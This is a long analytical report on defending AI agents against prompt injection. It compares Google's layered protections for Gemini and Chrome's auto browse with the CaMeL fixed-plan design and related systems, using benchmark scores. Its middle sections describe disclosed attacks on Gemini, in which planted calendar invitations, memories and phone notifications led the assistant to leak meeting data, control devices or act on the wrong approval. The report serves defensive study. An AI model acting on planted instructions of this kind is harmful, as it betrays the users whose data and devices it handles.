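Google launched auto browse as a preview for paying US subscribers on 28 January 2026, about seven weeks after Parker's post, according to Android Authority's *Chrome's latest feature lets you put your web browsing on autopilot* (2026). Google Cloud later said companies could turn it on for eligible Workspace users. Kanchwala (2026) reported in *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* that subscribers in India had it on desktop and Android by mid-October 2026.

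The critic appears to be part of the product. Berschadski, writing for business customers in August 2026, describes it in the present tense as working with auto browse. He is less definite about the restrictions on origins, writing that Google is "extending" the browser's site isolation to limit the agent to sites relevant to its task. Google's undated help page *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse* says Gemini already restricts itself to relevant websites and actions. Some restriction on sites is therefore in use, but neither document mentions a separate read-only list, so it is unknown whether Google has moved beyond the simpler version.

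Berschadski also describes tools that put the May 2025 principles into practice. Employees can interrupt the agent and follow its steps in a work log, and Chrome's history marks the pages the agent opened in the background. An agent can't open company data that its user isn't authorized to see. Companies can apply their data-loss rules, which block transfers of sensitive material, to agents' actions.

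The help page is a better guide than Berschadski's post to how far to trust the agent. Berschadski writes that the critic vetoes a hijacking attempt "instantly", which describes its speed but not how often it is right. The help page calls auto browse an "experimental feature" and gives much the same warnings about safeguards and supervision as the Spark help page. It also says the user is responsible for what Gemini does during a task, including unexpected purchases.

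The page also says that Gemini Spark can use auto browse in the user's own Chrome but may switch to a remote browser, for instance if the user closes the laptop before the task is finished. It doesn't say whether the critic and the origin limits also apply there. Parker and Berschadski both describe them as protections in Chrome, so they may not apply in the remote browser.

Google's *Mirror Dimension for Agents* describes testing auto browse on thousands of simulated websites, where engineers can plant injections without risk to real users. The agent sees the address of a real site, such as YouTube, while software supplies an imitation, because a model may behave differently when a site looks like a test. According to Mediasat's *Google создала изолированный интернет для проверки ИИ-агентов Chrome* (2026), the system produces more than 1,000 attack variants a day per engineer, over 30 times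 as many as manual work produces. Parker says his team uses attack success rates to judge its changes, but he doesn't publish any.

Chrome may later get firmer limits. In November 2026, Infobae's *Google prepara nuevas restricciones para frenar a los agentes de IA* reported that Google engineers wanted to build a prototype in which the browser enforces an agent's permissions. A user could let an agent visit a shop but forbid it to click or type there, and the restriction would hold even if the agent had no protections of its own. But once the user allowed clicking, the browser might not be able to tell whether a button continues or deletes something. Google hasn't said when, or whether, this will reach Chrome.

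### Chrome beside CaMeL

The table compares CaMeL with the full design for Chrome, including the read-only list that the first version lacked.

| | CaMeL | Chrome's auto browse |
|---|---|---|
| Who sees untrusted content | the quarantined model, which has no tools | the planner, which chooses each action |
| Who fixes the plan | the privileged model, before the agent opens outside content | nobody; the planner decides step by step |
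| What the system tracks | the sources and permitted readers of each value | the sites the agent may read and those it may act on |
| Final check on an action | code that applies a written policy, sometimes with a question to the user | a model, plus code for some sites and addresses, and the user for sensitive steps |
| What it guarantees | no tool calls outside the plan; protection of data only as good as the policies and tags | at most, no actions on sites outside the approved list; no assurance that the list or the action is right |

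Chrome's guarantee is weaker because many attacks start on sites that belong on the list. The review with the hidden instruction appears in the shop the user wanted to visit. Parker's team recognizes this, and its tests prioritize advertisements and user content on social media. A list of sites can stop the damage from spreading to the user's bank, but it can't prevent a harmful purchase in that shop.

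Tracking sites is also much less precise than tracking values. Suppose the user asks Gemini to find the dates of a trip in webmail and book a hotel. Webmail goes on the read-only list and the hotel on the read-writable list. The lists then allow the agent to type anything from the user's mail into the hotel's form, including a password-reset code. In CaMeL, the plan would pass the hotel check-in and check-out dates, and the interpreter would accept only values formatted as dates. An attacker could still make the dates wrong but couldn't pass the reset code in their place.

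The same problem arises when a site has many users. Chrome tracks which website receives the data but not which user, so an agent allowed to write to a marketplace may be able to message any seller there, including the attacker.

The UK's National Cyber Security Centre takes a position closer to CaMeL's on the final check. One of its technical directors, quoted in The Hacker News (2025), wants designers to focus more on "deterministic (non-LLM) safeguards that constrain the actions of the system". Chrome has some, such as the check on addresses, but leaves the hardest decision, whether an action is what the user wanted, to the critic. Making that decision with a rule in code would require a description of what each button on each website does, and no one has written one for the whole web.

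### Whether metadata can carry the attacker's address

The critic's protection depends on what its metadata contains, which Parker doesn't define. He says the critic sees no "unfiltered" untrustworthy content and that the web can't poison it "directly". Given those qualifications, attackers' text could still reach the critic after filtering or through the planner.

Suppose the user has the altered meeting notes open in Chrome and asks Gemini to send Bob the document through webmail. The planner reads the attacker's address in the notes, types it into the recipient field and proposes to click "Send". Origin Sets don't prevent this, because the task needs access to both the notes and the webmail site.

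If the metadata leaves out the text that the planner types, the critic sees only that Gemini is about to fill in a recipient and send an email. The user asked for exactly that, so the critic will probably approve it, whatever the address. If the metadata includes the address, the critic receives a value that the attacker chose and has nothing to compare it with, because the user's request names Bob but doesn't give his address. Like the Action Safety Agent, the critic may catch an obviously fake address, but a plausible one will probably pass.

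The critic is much more likely to catch the line that tells Gemini to forward the latest emails as well, because nothing in the request calls for a second email.

Longer values create another risk because the body of a message or a comment in a form, unlike an email address, has plenty of room for an argument. A manipulated planner could copy in a claim that the user has already approved the transfer, and the critic would read it if the metadata included that text. Google could reduce the risk by shortening or withholding such fields, but the critic would then have less information about what it was approving.

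Buttons raise the same difficulty, because the website's owner writes their labels. A dishonest shop could label a button "See sizes" when clicking it places an order. If the critic's description of a click relies on the label, the critic will approve what looks like a harmless step. Google treats labels as a possible route for attacks, since its simulated websites can include malicious labels in the hidden form that screen readers use. Google's public descriptions don't explain how the critic determines what a click will do.

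Adding CaMeL's tags to the metadata, such as "copied from shared notes", would be very useful but hard. The planner is a language model that takes in the whole page and produces new text, and ordinary software can't tell which words on the page led to which words in the output. To be safe, Chrome would have to treat everything the planner wrote after its first untrusted page as untrusted. CaMeL can be more selective because its interpreter, not a model, passes values from step to step.

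Chrome could recover some of this precision without tags if software checked for the recipient's address in the user's request and contacts, and asked the user to confirm only when it appeared in neither. Neither Parker nor Berschadski describes such a check. In Chrome as they describe it, the false address would probably reach the confirmation question, which, according to the help page, Gemini "aims to ask" before it sends a message.

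## Whether the layers hold against real attackers

Google accepts that some injections will get past each of Gemini's layers. It considers this tolerable if attacks require enough resources, while Willison thinks almost any remaining failure rate means the defenses have failed.

### The dispute over 99 percent

Willison judges these defenses by a standard from web security. He argues that if programmers had protected websites against SQL injection with methods that failed 1 percent of the time, attackers would have broken into those sites within moments. In *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems*, he applied this standard to Google DeepMind's work with automated attacks and called a filter that catches 99 percent of attacks "effectively worthless". In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, he was just as suspicious of security products that claim to catch 95 percent.

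Google DeepMind expected no single defense to solve prompt injection and proposed combining automated testing, monitoring, heuristic defenses and standard security engineering. Willison agreed that a single solution looked unlikely, but he doubted that heuristics would make vulnerable systems safe enough to deploy responsibly.

In its June 2025 post, Google argues that its layered defenses force attackers to use methods that are easier to identify or that take more resources. An attack may still work technically but fail because it costs the attacker more than it brings in.

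Some invented figures show when this argument works. Suppose a criminal spends $20,000 finding an email that gets through the layers, the email works on 1 percent of recipients, and each success is worth $50. The criminal has to reach 40,000 people to break even (20,000 ÷ (0.01 × 50)). If Google usually notices such a campaign and blocks the email after 10,000 copies, the criminal can expect to earn only $5,000 and has no reason to start. But a spy who values one executive's mail at $5 million would pay the same $20,000 for a 1 percent chance of getting it, since that chance is worth $50,000.

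Raising attackers' costs therefore works best against mass attacks for small gains, and much of the protection comes from noticing the campaign early. It gives the least protection to the people whose data is most valuable. Even if a criminal misjudged the costs and lost money on an attack, about 100 people would still lose their data.

In *Invitation Is All You Need*, Ben Nassi, Stav Cohen and Or Yair estimated that a computer science graduate with an ordinary laptop could prepare most of their attacks on Gemini in less than a day. Against the full set of defenses they recommend, they thought an attacker would need expertise in AI, a cluster of specialized processors, detailed knowledge of the defenses, and several months. If that is right, layers greatly increase the initial effort an attack requires. But the researchers didn't test the estimate, and the defenses they recommend differ from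 Google's.

Tests of other defenses are less encouraging. *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper (cited in Willison, 2025), reports attacks that broke most of the twelve published defenses it examined, with success rates above 90 percent.

Willison's standard is also hard for CaMeL to meet wherever it relies on the user's approval, because even careful people approve things they shouldn't. Willison mentions that Troy Hunt, a well-known security researcher, fell for a phishing email in 2025 while jet-lagged. Nobody expects a person to catch 99 percent of bad requests. CaMeL's advantage is that many attacks fail before the user is asked to approve anything.

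### Disclosed flaws in Gemini

**Calendar invitations, 2025.** Nassi, Cohen and Yair planted instructions in the titles of calendar invitations and, in some tests, in the subject lines of emails. The victim only had to ask Gemini about upcoming events or recent mail. In tests on the researchers' own accounts, Gemini read out abuse, recommended an investment, deleted a meeting, turned on a boiler, opened a window, and put the user on a Zoom video call. In one test, it sent the titles of six meetings to a server's owner by opening a web address that contained them.

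Google had already split Gemini into several agents, such as one for the calendar and one for the home, each with a private working context. Only a coordinating model could start another agent. But the calendar agent had to send its results to that model, and the results contained the planted text. That text included an instruction for the coordinating model to wait for the user's next message, such as "thanks", before acting, which security researchers call *delayed tool invocation*.

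The separation between agents clearly failed. It's harder to tell whether the other layers failed too, because the paper says the five protections Google later described "were ineffective or weren't deployed" during the study. Google received the report on 22 February 2025. In a statement in late June, it said it had extended user confirmation to risky operations involving Workspace data, other apps and devices, and had added a content classifier and better detection of suspicious links. Google called the attacks "theoretical", although the researchers had recorded them on video.

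**False memories, 2025.** The same paper describes earlier work by Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who used an injection to plant false information in Gemini's long-term memory. Gemini uses this memory in later conversations, so one successful injection can keep misleading the user after the original document is gone. Nassi and colleagues recommend barring Gemini from updating its memory after it has read outside data. Google didn't mention memory in its June statement, so it is unclear which of its fixes, if any, covers this attack.

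**Calendar invitations, January 2026.** The security company Miggo found another calendar attack, this time using an instruction in an invitation's description. According to The Hacker News (2026), the instruction took effect when Gemini processed it, exposing private meeting data and creating deceptive events without any direct action by the user. The attack used Google Calendar to get the data out.

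*Miggo Security bypasses Google Gemini defenses via calendar invites* (Çıtak, 2026) reports that Miggo's attack got past Google's separate model for detecting malicious prompts, and past the defenses Google had added after the 2025 research. The instruction was in ordinary language, which gives a classifier little to detect. Confirmation evidently didn't stop the attack either, so Gemini could apparently create an event without asking the user. Google fixed the flaw after Miggo reported it.

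**Android notifications, June 2026.** In the latest case found, messages from ordinary chat apps could inject instructions through a phone's notifications, Fadilpašić (2026) reported in *Hackers could use poisoned WhatsApp and Slack notifications*. The security company SafeBreach, where Yair worked when he co-wrote the 2025 paper, discovered the flaw.

SC Media's *Android Gemini prompt injection flaw patched by Google* describes an attack in which the user asks Gemini to read out the pending notifications. One notification contains a command in a language the user doesn't understand, along with a harmless question. When the user answers "yes" to the question, Gemini treats this as approval of the command. *谷歌Gemini语音助理曝漏洞，黑客利用特殊构造通知信息为AI“下毒”* (2026), from the Chinese technology site IT之家, describes another version, which hides the real question in a link that Gemini doesn't read aloud.

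SC Media says an attacker could obtain the user's contacts, while IT之家 says an attacker could change the phone numbers in them and control devices in the home. In both accounts, the confirmation layer failed because the user had said yes to something other than the attacker's action. Google had strengthened that layer only months earlier in response to the invitation attacks.

SafeBreach reported the attack to Google in August 2025, and Google made a change on its servers in November. According to IT之家, the change improved the content classifier. That would make such notifications less likely to reach Gemini, but it wouldn't tie the user's "yes" to one particular action. If Google changed nothing else, an attacker who finds text the classifier misses could try the same trick again.

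No reports of criminals using any of these four flaws have been found.

### The same attacks under CaMeL

The verdicts in this table come from applying CaMeL's published rules to attacks that researchers carried out on Gemini. No test of these attacks on CaMeL itself has been found. The verdicts assume that the user makes the same request as in the original attack and that the planted text never reaches the privileged model.

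| Attack | Kind of harm | Would CaMeL stop it? | Policy needed if the plan includes the same tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Invitations: devices, Zoom, deleted meetings | action | yes | no untrusted data may decide which device, call or meeting is affected |
| Invitations: meeting titles sent in a web address | action | yes | private data may go only to sites allowed to read it |
| Invitations: abuse, investment advice, phishing links | misleading text | no | none, since there is no tool call to check |
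| False memories | an action, then misleading text | yes, the saving | only information from the user may be saved |
| Miggo's calendar attack | action | yes | an event may contain only data that everyone who can see it may read |
| Notifications | action | probably | the user must approve the exact action |

Most of the verdicts are the same because the users had only asked Gemini to read something. To answer "What are my events this week?", CaMeL's plan would fetch the events, have the quarantined model summarize them, and display the summary. The plan would contain no call that opens a window or creates an event, so control-flow integrity would stop these actions even without any policies.

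By this test, CaMeL would stop 10 of the 14 scenarios in *Invitation Is All You Need*, assuming the request didn't call for the harmful action. The other four are abuse, spam, phishing and disinformation, which harm the user through text. CaMeL could still prevent the disinformation from entering Gemini's memory, but not from appearing in a single answer. (The researchers argued that phishing and a self-spreading email worm were possible but didn't run either attack, and they left the disinformation to Rehberger's earlier demonstration.)

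None of these attacks depends on a changed value like the false address for Bob, so a fixed plan would have been enough to stop them without CaMeL's tags. The tags may still be necessary, because attackers who can make Gemini open a window don't need a subtler method, but would need one if Google blocked this one.

In Miggo's attack, the tags become important as soon as the user asks for more. If the user asks the assistant to schedule a meeting and write a short description based on earlier meetings, the plan has to create an event, and a planted instruction could make the quarantined model fill the description with private details from other meetings. Control-flow integrity would not prevent this, because creating the event is part of the plan. Only a policy that compares who can read the earlier meetings with who can read the new event would block it.

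The assumption about the privileged model is harder to satisfy in a conversation than in a single request. In the invitation and notification attacks, Gemini acted only after the user's next message. If CaMeL treated a "thanks" or "yes" as a new request and gave the privileged model the whole conversation, text planted in the previous answer could influence the new plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues found this kind of boundary laundering between agents, and here it would happen between two turns of one conversation.

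A careful implementation could show the privileged model only what the user wrote and variable names for earlier results. A bare "yes" would then approve a tool call only if the interpreter had prompted the user about that call. That would stop the notification attack but make some ordinary conversations awkward. If a friend's message reads "Are you coming at seven?", the user may well say "yes" and expect the assistant to reply to the friend.

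Memory raises the same problem over a longer period. If the privileged model treats saved memories as trusted facts about the user, one planted memory can influence every later plan. To prevent this, CaMeL would have to preserve each memory's tags between sessions or keep memories from outside sources away from the privileged model.

Nassi and colleagues propose simpler rules that would give some of the same protection. For example, the assistant could run a request twice, once with the outside data and once without it, and ask the user to confirm if the resulting actions differ. This would have caught the window and video call attacks, because neither "What are my events?" nor "thanks" normally leads to those actions. The assistant would also ask for confirmation whenever the user wants outside content to determine the action, such as when paying an invoice.

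### Injections on the public web

Researchers can show which attacks are possible, but not which ones criminals are trying. Google searched the public web for injections and published the results. Search Engine World's *Google Says Prompt Injection Moving From Theory Into Real Abuse* gives the publication date as 23 April 2026. The search used Common Crawl, an archive that takes monthly snapshots of 2 to 3 billion pages, mostly static ones such as blogs, forums and comment sections.

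Google first searched for familiar phrases that tell an AI to ignore its instructions. It then used Gemini to assess the purpose of the matching text and whether it was out of place on the page, and people reviewed the results. These steps were needed because most of the initial matches were harmless, such as research papers and articles about prompt injection.

Many of the real injections were pranks, such as hidden text telling an assistant to change its tone. Some website owners wanted to add context to AI summaries or promote their business over competitors. Others wanted to keep AI agents away, and one tried to send agents to a page that never finishes loading. Google found only a few attempts to steal data and considered them unsophisticated. It also found commands to delete all the files on the user's computer, but thought they were unlikely to work.

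Google didn't find significant numbers of the advanced attacks that researchers had published in 2025, and it concluded that criminals had not yet used that research on a large scale. This partly supports its economic argument, since nearly everyone who could have copied those attacks to a website apparently hadn't bothered. But Google searched for known phrases, and it acknowledges that it may have missed unusual ones. An instruction in ordinary language, like the one Miggo used, would probably not have matched. The method therefore finds crude attacks more easily than good ones, so it may understate attackers' skill.

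Malicious injections rose by 32 percent between November 2025 and February 2026. At that rate, they would roughly triple in a year (1.32⁴ ≈ 3.0), but three months is a short period to project from. Google also gives no absolute numbers, so the rise could have been from 25 pages to 33 or from 25,000 to 33,000.

Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* reports that researchers at the security company Forcepoint also published evidence that same week of real injections on public websites.

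These findings matter most for Chrome's agent, which reads such pages. They provide little information about attacks on Gemini in Workspace. In the four disclosed flaws, researchers planted the instructions in private emails, invitations, shared documents or phone notifications, which Common Crawl doesn't contain. Common Crawl also leaves out most social media, which Google plans to study separately.

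Google expects attacks to become more common and sophisticated. It reasons that attackers weigh effort against reward, that more capable agents are more valuable targets, and that attackers are using AI to automate their work. This complicates its economic argument for the layers, because if working injections become easier to find and more valuable, Google has to keep improving the layers just to deter the same attackers.

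### Why the flaws give no failure rate

Disclosed flaws don't show what share of real attacks gets through Gemini's layers, because researchers usually leave out their failed attempts and criminals don't publish any of theirs. A researcher who succeeded on the fifth try may publish much the same report as one who needed 5,000 tries.

The number of disclosures isn't a good measure of security either. It can rise because Gemini has become less secure, but also because Google pays researchers more for reporting flaws or connects the assistant to more apps. A year without disclosures could mean the defenses are strong or that researchers were focused on other companies' products.

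The most prominent number in *Invitation Is All You Need* is 73 percent, the share of analyzed threats that it says pose a high to critical risk to users. This figure is based on the researchers' ratings of likelihood and impact and doesn't measure how often attacks succeed. The ratings listed in the paper's text actually give 10 threats out of 14, or 71 percent.

The lack of known criminal use is also weak evidence of safety. Someone whose meeting titles leaked in a web address might never notice, and might not suspect the calendar invitation even if the information later turned up elsewhere. Google can search its logs for signs of abuse, but in its statement on the invitation attacks, Google doesn't say whether it did or what it found.

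The disclosures are better evidence of how long users remained exposed. Google announced its fixes for the invitation attacks about four months after receiving the report and took about three months to fix the notification flaw. Some protections may have arrived earlier, and there is no sign that anyone exploited the flaws in the meantime. But an attacker who found either flaw independently would have had months to use it, which is a long time for a defense that relies on making attacks unprofitable. The point fixes that Gavish describes are meant to shorten this delay. Both repairs came before his April 2026 post, so they don't show how quickly Google can respond now.

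## What CaMeL's guarantees cost in usefulness

A fixed plan would have stopped most of the attacks researchers carried out on Gemini, but it also prevents the assistant from adapting when an email or web page contains something unexpected. People often use an assistant because they haven't read the email yet, so it is unclear whether CaMeL could run a general assistant or only a narrow one.

### 77 percent of the tasks

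Most of the evidence comes from *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark that two of CaMeL's designers helped create. It launched with 97 tasks and 629 security test cases in a simulated office, bank, travel service and Slack workspace. In a typical task, the agent must summarize the unread emails and forward the summary to the team lead.

Each security case pairs a task with an attacker's goal, such as sending the user's calendar to an outside server. The planted instruction is placed where a stranger's text would normally appear, such as the body of an email. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) explains that after the agent finishes, ordinary software checks the simulated environment to see whether the email was sent or the money was transferred, so the result doesn't depend on grading by another model.

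The benchmark scores completed tasks and successful attacks separately. According to the revised CaMeL paper, CaMeL solved 77 percent of the tasks with its security guarantees, compared with 84 percent for an undefended system. This is a net loss of roughly one in 12 tasks that the undefended system could do.

Early reports give 67 percent, the score in the paper's first version from March 2025, and Tallam and Miller still used it that July. Both 67 and 77 percent are shares of tasks completed. An agent that refused every request would score zero on this measure while blocking every attack, so neither score means that CaMeL lets a quarter or a third of attacks through.

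Garby and colleagues report that only two attacks succeeded in the paper's own evaluation. In one, the user had told the agent to make a payment as a document directed, a case CaMeL's designers consider outside the threats it addresses. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the scoring software counted the quoted text as a successful attack.

### Why other tests give different scores

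CaMeL's score depends heavily on the model that writes the plans. In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) cite CaMeL's published AgentDojo score with GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, as 53.6 percent. They measured 83.0 percent for the same model without a defense.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested newer models on two benchmarks in systems where several agents share the work. AssetOpsBench has tasks about industrial equipment, and MultiAgentDojo divides AgentDojo's tools among specialized agents. Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks.

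| Test | Model | Undefended | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, from Bhagwatkar and colleagues | GPT-4o | 83.0% | 53.6% |
| AssetOpsBench, no policies, from Peters-Gill and colleagues | GPT-5.5 | 87.5% | 82.1% |
| AssetOpsBench, no policies | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% | 55.4% |
| MultiAgentDojo, no policies | GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% |
| MultiAgentDojo, no policies | Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3% | 42.3% |
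| AgentDojo banking, no policies, from Garby and colleagues | GPT-5.2 | no figure | 66.7% |
| AgentDojo banking, with policies | GPT-5.2 | no figure | 37.5% |

Writing a whole program in advance is harder than choosing one step at a time, and weaker models lose more performance from it. On AssetOpsBench, the small Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite fell from 64.3 to 20.5 percent. The average loss was 21.6 points across five models and 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The pattern isn't entirely regular, since Fable 5 lost 21.4 points, but it suggests that CaMeL will lower scores less as models improve, even if its design doesn't change.

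CaMeL's lowest score on the full AgentDojo benchmark comes from *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defense. In its rerun, CaMeL solved only 29 of the 97 tasks, though none of the 629 attacks succeeded. The rerun connected CaMeL's released code to the benchmark through an adapter, which may explain part of the low score.

CaMeL's disadvantage can disappear under attack. When the data contained injections, CaMeL completed 54.5 percent of its tasks, while an undefended GPT-4o completed 50.0 percent. With these figures, CaMeL would complete more tasks overall only if at least 87 percent of them were under attack. Few people face attacks that often, so most users will complete fewer tasks with CaMeL, and the reason to use it is the harm it prevents.

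CaMeL also uses more computing. The CaMeL paper puts the overhead at 2.82 times the input tokens and 2.73 times the output tokens. Tallam and Miller estimate that a quarantined model could take more than ten seconds to read ten emails, based on GPT-4 taking one to two seconds per request. Using a newer model or reading the emails in parallel could shorten that time.

Tallam and Miller suggest reusing plans for common requests, replacing the quarantined model with ordinary software where the data has a regular format, and extracting values from many documents in one request. They say the first two together halved the tokens and delay in the best case, but they base this on internal tests that they don't describe. If 100 receipts share one prompt, a malicious instruction in one of them could also change the amounts that the model reports for the other 99.

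### Writing the policies, and living with them

CaMeL's policy checks account for much of the lost usefulness in the banking test. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5.2, it completed 32 of 48 runs with the checks off and 18 with them on. With a second model, MiMo-v2.5, completed runs fell from 34 to 18. The samples are small, but both models lost nearly half of their completed runs.

For example, a user might ask the agent to pay a bill saved as a file. The plan reads the account number from the file and passes it to the payment tool. A strict policy allows payments only to accounts from a trusted source, and a file isn't one, so the interpreter blocks the payment. A looser policy would allow the payment, but an attacker who had altered the bill could then collect the money.

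The same thing happened with TypeGuard, another system that enforces rules on data flows. It solved 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks without its policies and 8 with them. CaMeL solved 7 with policies active. The TypeGuard paper says that many of the tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit" and suggests asking the user. If the user could approve the bill's account number, the payment would go through, so a real product would ask the user about some of these cases instead of failing.

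Somebody also has to write and update the policies. AgentDojo's simulated office has 24 tools: nine for email, seven for the calendar and eight for files. Tallam and Miller warn that a company with hundreds of tools would end up with duplicated and inconsistent rules that nobody audits as a whole. They recommend a dedicated policy language, in which a company could write a rule such as "share only within our domain" once and apply it to every tool.

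That would save work, but someone would still have to decide what each rule should allow. A company's security staff can decide which employees may see the salary file. People who use Gemini at home have no security staff, and Google can't know that one user's accountant should receive tax documents while another's former accountant should not. Google could start with strict defaults and learn from the user's answers, but then the assistant would ask the most questions in the first weeks, when new users are deciding whether it is worth using.

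### When every question gets a yes

Frequent approval requests weaken the protection they are meant to provide. If an assistant asked for approval 20 times a day and one request in 5,000 hid an attack, the user would see an attack about once every 250 days, after approving thousands of harmless requests. Few people would still be reading each request carefully by then. Tallam and Miller call this *prompt fatigue*.

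As a remedy, they propose sorting actions by risk. Reading public or openly shared information, such as a list of calendar events, would need only a basic check of where the data came from. Changes within the user's own files would need a quick confirmation if they depended on untrusted data. Irreversible or external actions, such as emails and bank transfers, would go through CaMeL's full checks and need a stronger approval, for example with a second device.

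Tallam and Miller didn't test this scheme on AgentDojo, and its categories need to be drawn carefully. They give moving a file to a shared folder as an example of a change that needs only a quick confirmation, but this could reveal a salary file to everyone with access to that folder. The scheme also does little for people who mostly use their assistant to send email, because every message falls into the strictest category.

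CaMeL's tags can reduce the number of questions users must answer, but the remaining questions are an important part of the lost usefulness, and a score for completed tasks doesn't count them.

### "Do what this email asks"

Better policies don't help when the user leaves the choice of action to the content. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) sorts requests by how much they leave open. A request can give both the action and the details, as in "send the draft proposal to bob@client.example". It can name the action but leave the details to the content, as with Bob's document, where the name and address are in the notes. Or it can leave the action to the content too, as in "do what Anna's email asks".

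CaMeL's privileged model has to write a program for Anna's email without reading it. She may want last month's figures, a meeting on Tuesday, or both. The privileged model could write a program that covers many possibilities:

```
email = find_latest_email(sender = "Anna")
steps = ask_quarantined("List the actions this email asks for.",
                        email, format = ListOfSteps)
for step in steps:
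    if step.tool == "send_email":
        send_email(to = step.recipient, attachment = step.file)
    if step.tool == "create_event":
        create_event(title = step.title, time = step.time)
    if step.tool == "delete_file":
        delete_file(name = step.file)
```

This program technically has control-flow integrity, because the privileged model wrote every line in advance. But whoever wrote the email chooses which tools run, in what order and with what values. If someone has broken into Anna's account, they control the assistant almost as completely as they would without CaMeL.

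Garby and colleagues saw this happen in one of AgentDojo's banking tasks, which is to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The model wrote a loop with a branch for each tool. Two attacks got through this way when the policy checks were off, but no attack succeeded in the runs that finished with the checks on. However, policies strict enough to stop a hostile instruction will usually stop Anna's genuine requests too.

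The safest alternative is for the assistant to show the email to the user, who then replies, "Send her the March figures and book Tuesday at ten." CaMeL can easily plan from that instruction. This adds only one message, but the user must read the email and work out what to do, which is the task they wanted to hand over.

Layered defenses aren't safe either when the user leaves the action open. Ma and colleagues tested ten defenses and found that attacks succeeded much more often on such requests. So other agents complete some of the tasks that CaMeL fails, but only by taking a large risk. These tasks still matter because, as Ma and colleagues also point out, people typically delegate details and don't spell out every step.

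### A website the planner has never seen

Browsing the web with a fixed plan is difficult even when the user's request is clear. In one task from OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks on a real computer desktop, an agent must reach the natural products section of drugs.com. No button leads directly there, so an ordinary agent looks at the menus, tries a likely one and goes back if it was wrong.

CaMeL's planner has to plan for all of this before the site opens. The program might close a cookie notice if one appears, look for a link about natural products, open the main menu if there isn't one, and use the search box if the menu doesn't help. If the section is listed under a heading the plan doesn't cover, the program runs out of branches and the task fails, even though the right link may be on the screen the model is reading.

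*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* found that CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo averaged 52 lines of code, with about five tool calls and four branches. Its best plans for OSWorld averaged 213 lines, with about 40 tool calls and 40 branches, and about half of their steps were fallbacks that didn't run.

In Peters-Gill and colleagues' tests, too, most of CaMeL's failures came from committing to a plan before seeing the data. Sometimes the need for another step became clear only after a tool returned its result. In other cases the program continued when it should have stopped. An agent asked for one period's data on a piece of equipment would return data from a nearby period, and the parent agent's program, written earlier, would use it without detecting the mismatch. The user then gets a wrong answer with no sign that anything failed.

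### Designs that try to lower the price

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* makes fixed plans more practical by giving the planner a routine for checking the screen before each action. The program has one model describe the screen and another check the description against a specific expectation, such as "a cookie notice is visible", then takes the branch for that answer. The planner's instructions already cover common problems, such as cookie notices and failed clicks, which leaves the planner mainly to handle the user's task.

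On 60 tasks that a small model could do without protection, adding the routine to basic CaMeL raised the number solved in up to three attempts from 11 to 35. On 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 could do unprotected, the version with the routine solved 31 at the first attempt and 62 in up to five. The paper's claim that the design retains up to 57 percent of performance is based on the five-attempt result. Relying on several attempts requires a way to recognize which one was right, and a failed attempt may already have sent an email or bought a ticket. For tasks with such effects, the first-attempt score of 28 percent is more realistic.

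The paper also adapted Fides, a Microsoft design that calls the planner again after every step but hides the tools' output from it. Fides solved about as many of the 60 tasks as CaMeL within five attempts (67 percent against 65), but fewer on the first attempt (33 percent against 42). Fides sent the planner the full history each time, so it used 29.6 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent, while CaMeL used 1.88 times as many. Planning step by step helped little here when the planner still had no access to the page's contents.

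Garby and colleagues took a different approach with an agent called Randori. Its planner first tests its program in an artificial world, where errors can't reveal the user's secrets or send anything twice, so the model can repair the program before it touches real data. The program may also *endorse* a particular piece of untrusted data, which means declaring that it will treat that data as trusted. To pay a bill, for instance, it could endorse the account number in the file the user named.

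With GPT-5.2 and all its rules active, Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL with policies. Across three models, the attacker succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, which the attacker had replaced with a false payment request. Without endorsement, Randori blocked that attack, but its completed runs with another model, Qwen3.7-plus, fell from 36 to 30. Endorsement therefore lets Randori complete more tasks but weakens protection at known points in the program. The planner could endorse too much, though it has to decide before it sees any of the attacker's text.

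Other systems don't use a fixed plan. SecureClaw lets the model choose its next step after reading each result and checks the model's actions separately. It solved 59 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks, twice as many as CaMeL in the same comparison. Its attack success rate was low but still above CaMeL's zero. TypeGuard and a similar system, Tacit, let the agent write new code after reading untrusted data but check that code against strict rules. Tacit stopped all but one of 1,926 attacks.

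These systems depend more on their rules than CaMeL does. Of the 144 combinations of task and attack in AgentDojo's banking tests, there are 97 in which the attack needs an action that would never appear in a plan for the user's task. A fixed plan generally stops these attacks even if nobody has written a policy. In a system without a fixed plan, a missing or faulty rule could let any of the 144 through.

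*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injection* recommends limiting what each agent can do and accepting the loss of generality. An agent that only books trips has a few tools and predictable steps, so its developers can write good policies and foresee most branches. This advice makes sense for a company building a booking agent, but it doesn't help Google much with an assistant that is supposed to handle whatever the user asks for.

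### What the layers cost, and why no scale fits both

Gemini's layered defenses also make it less useful. One malicious email can make Gemini withhold a summary, consequential actions need the user's confirmation, and Chrome restricts the agent to certain sites. Google doesn't appear to have published the share of ordinary tasks that Gemini completes with and without these protections, so comparing CaMeL's 77 percent with an assumed 100 percent for Gemini would be unfair to CaMeL.

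Tests of defenses similar to Google's suggest that they can make an agent much less useful. Bhagwatkar and colleagues found that adding an injection detector to GPT-4o cut its AgentDojo score from 83.0 to 41.5 percent, below CaMeL's 53.6. Spotlighting reduced it to 71.7 percent. Repeating the user's request in the prompt did not measurably lower the score, but 27.8 percent of attacks still succeeded. None of these defenses is Google's own version, and a better detector would block fewer harmless emails.

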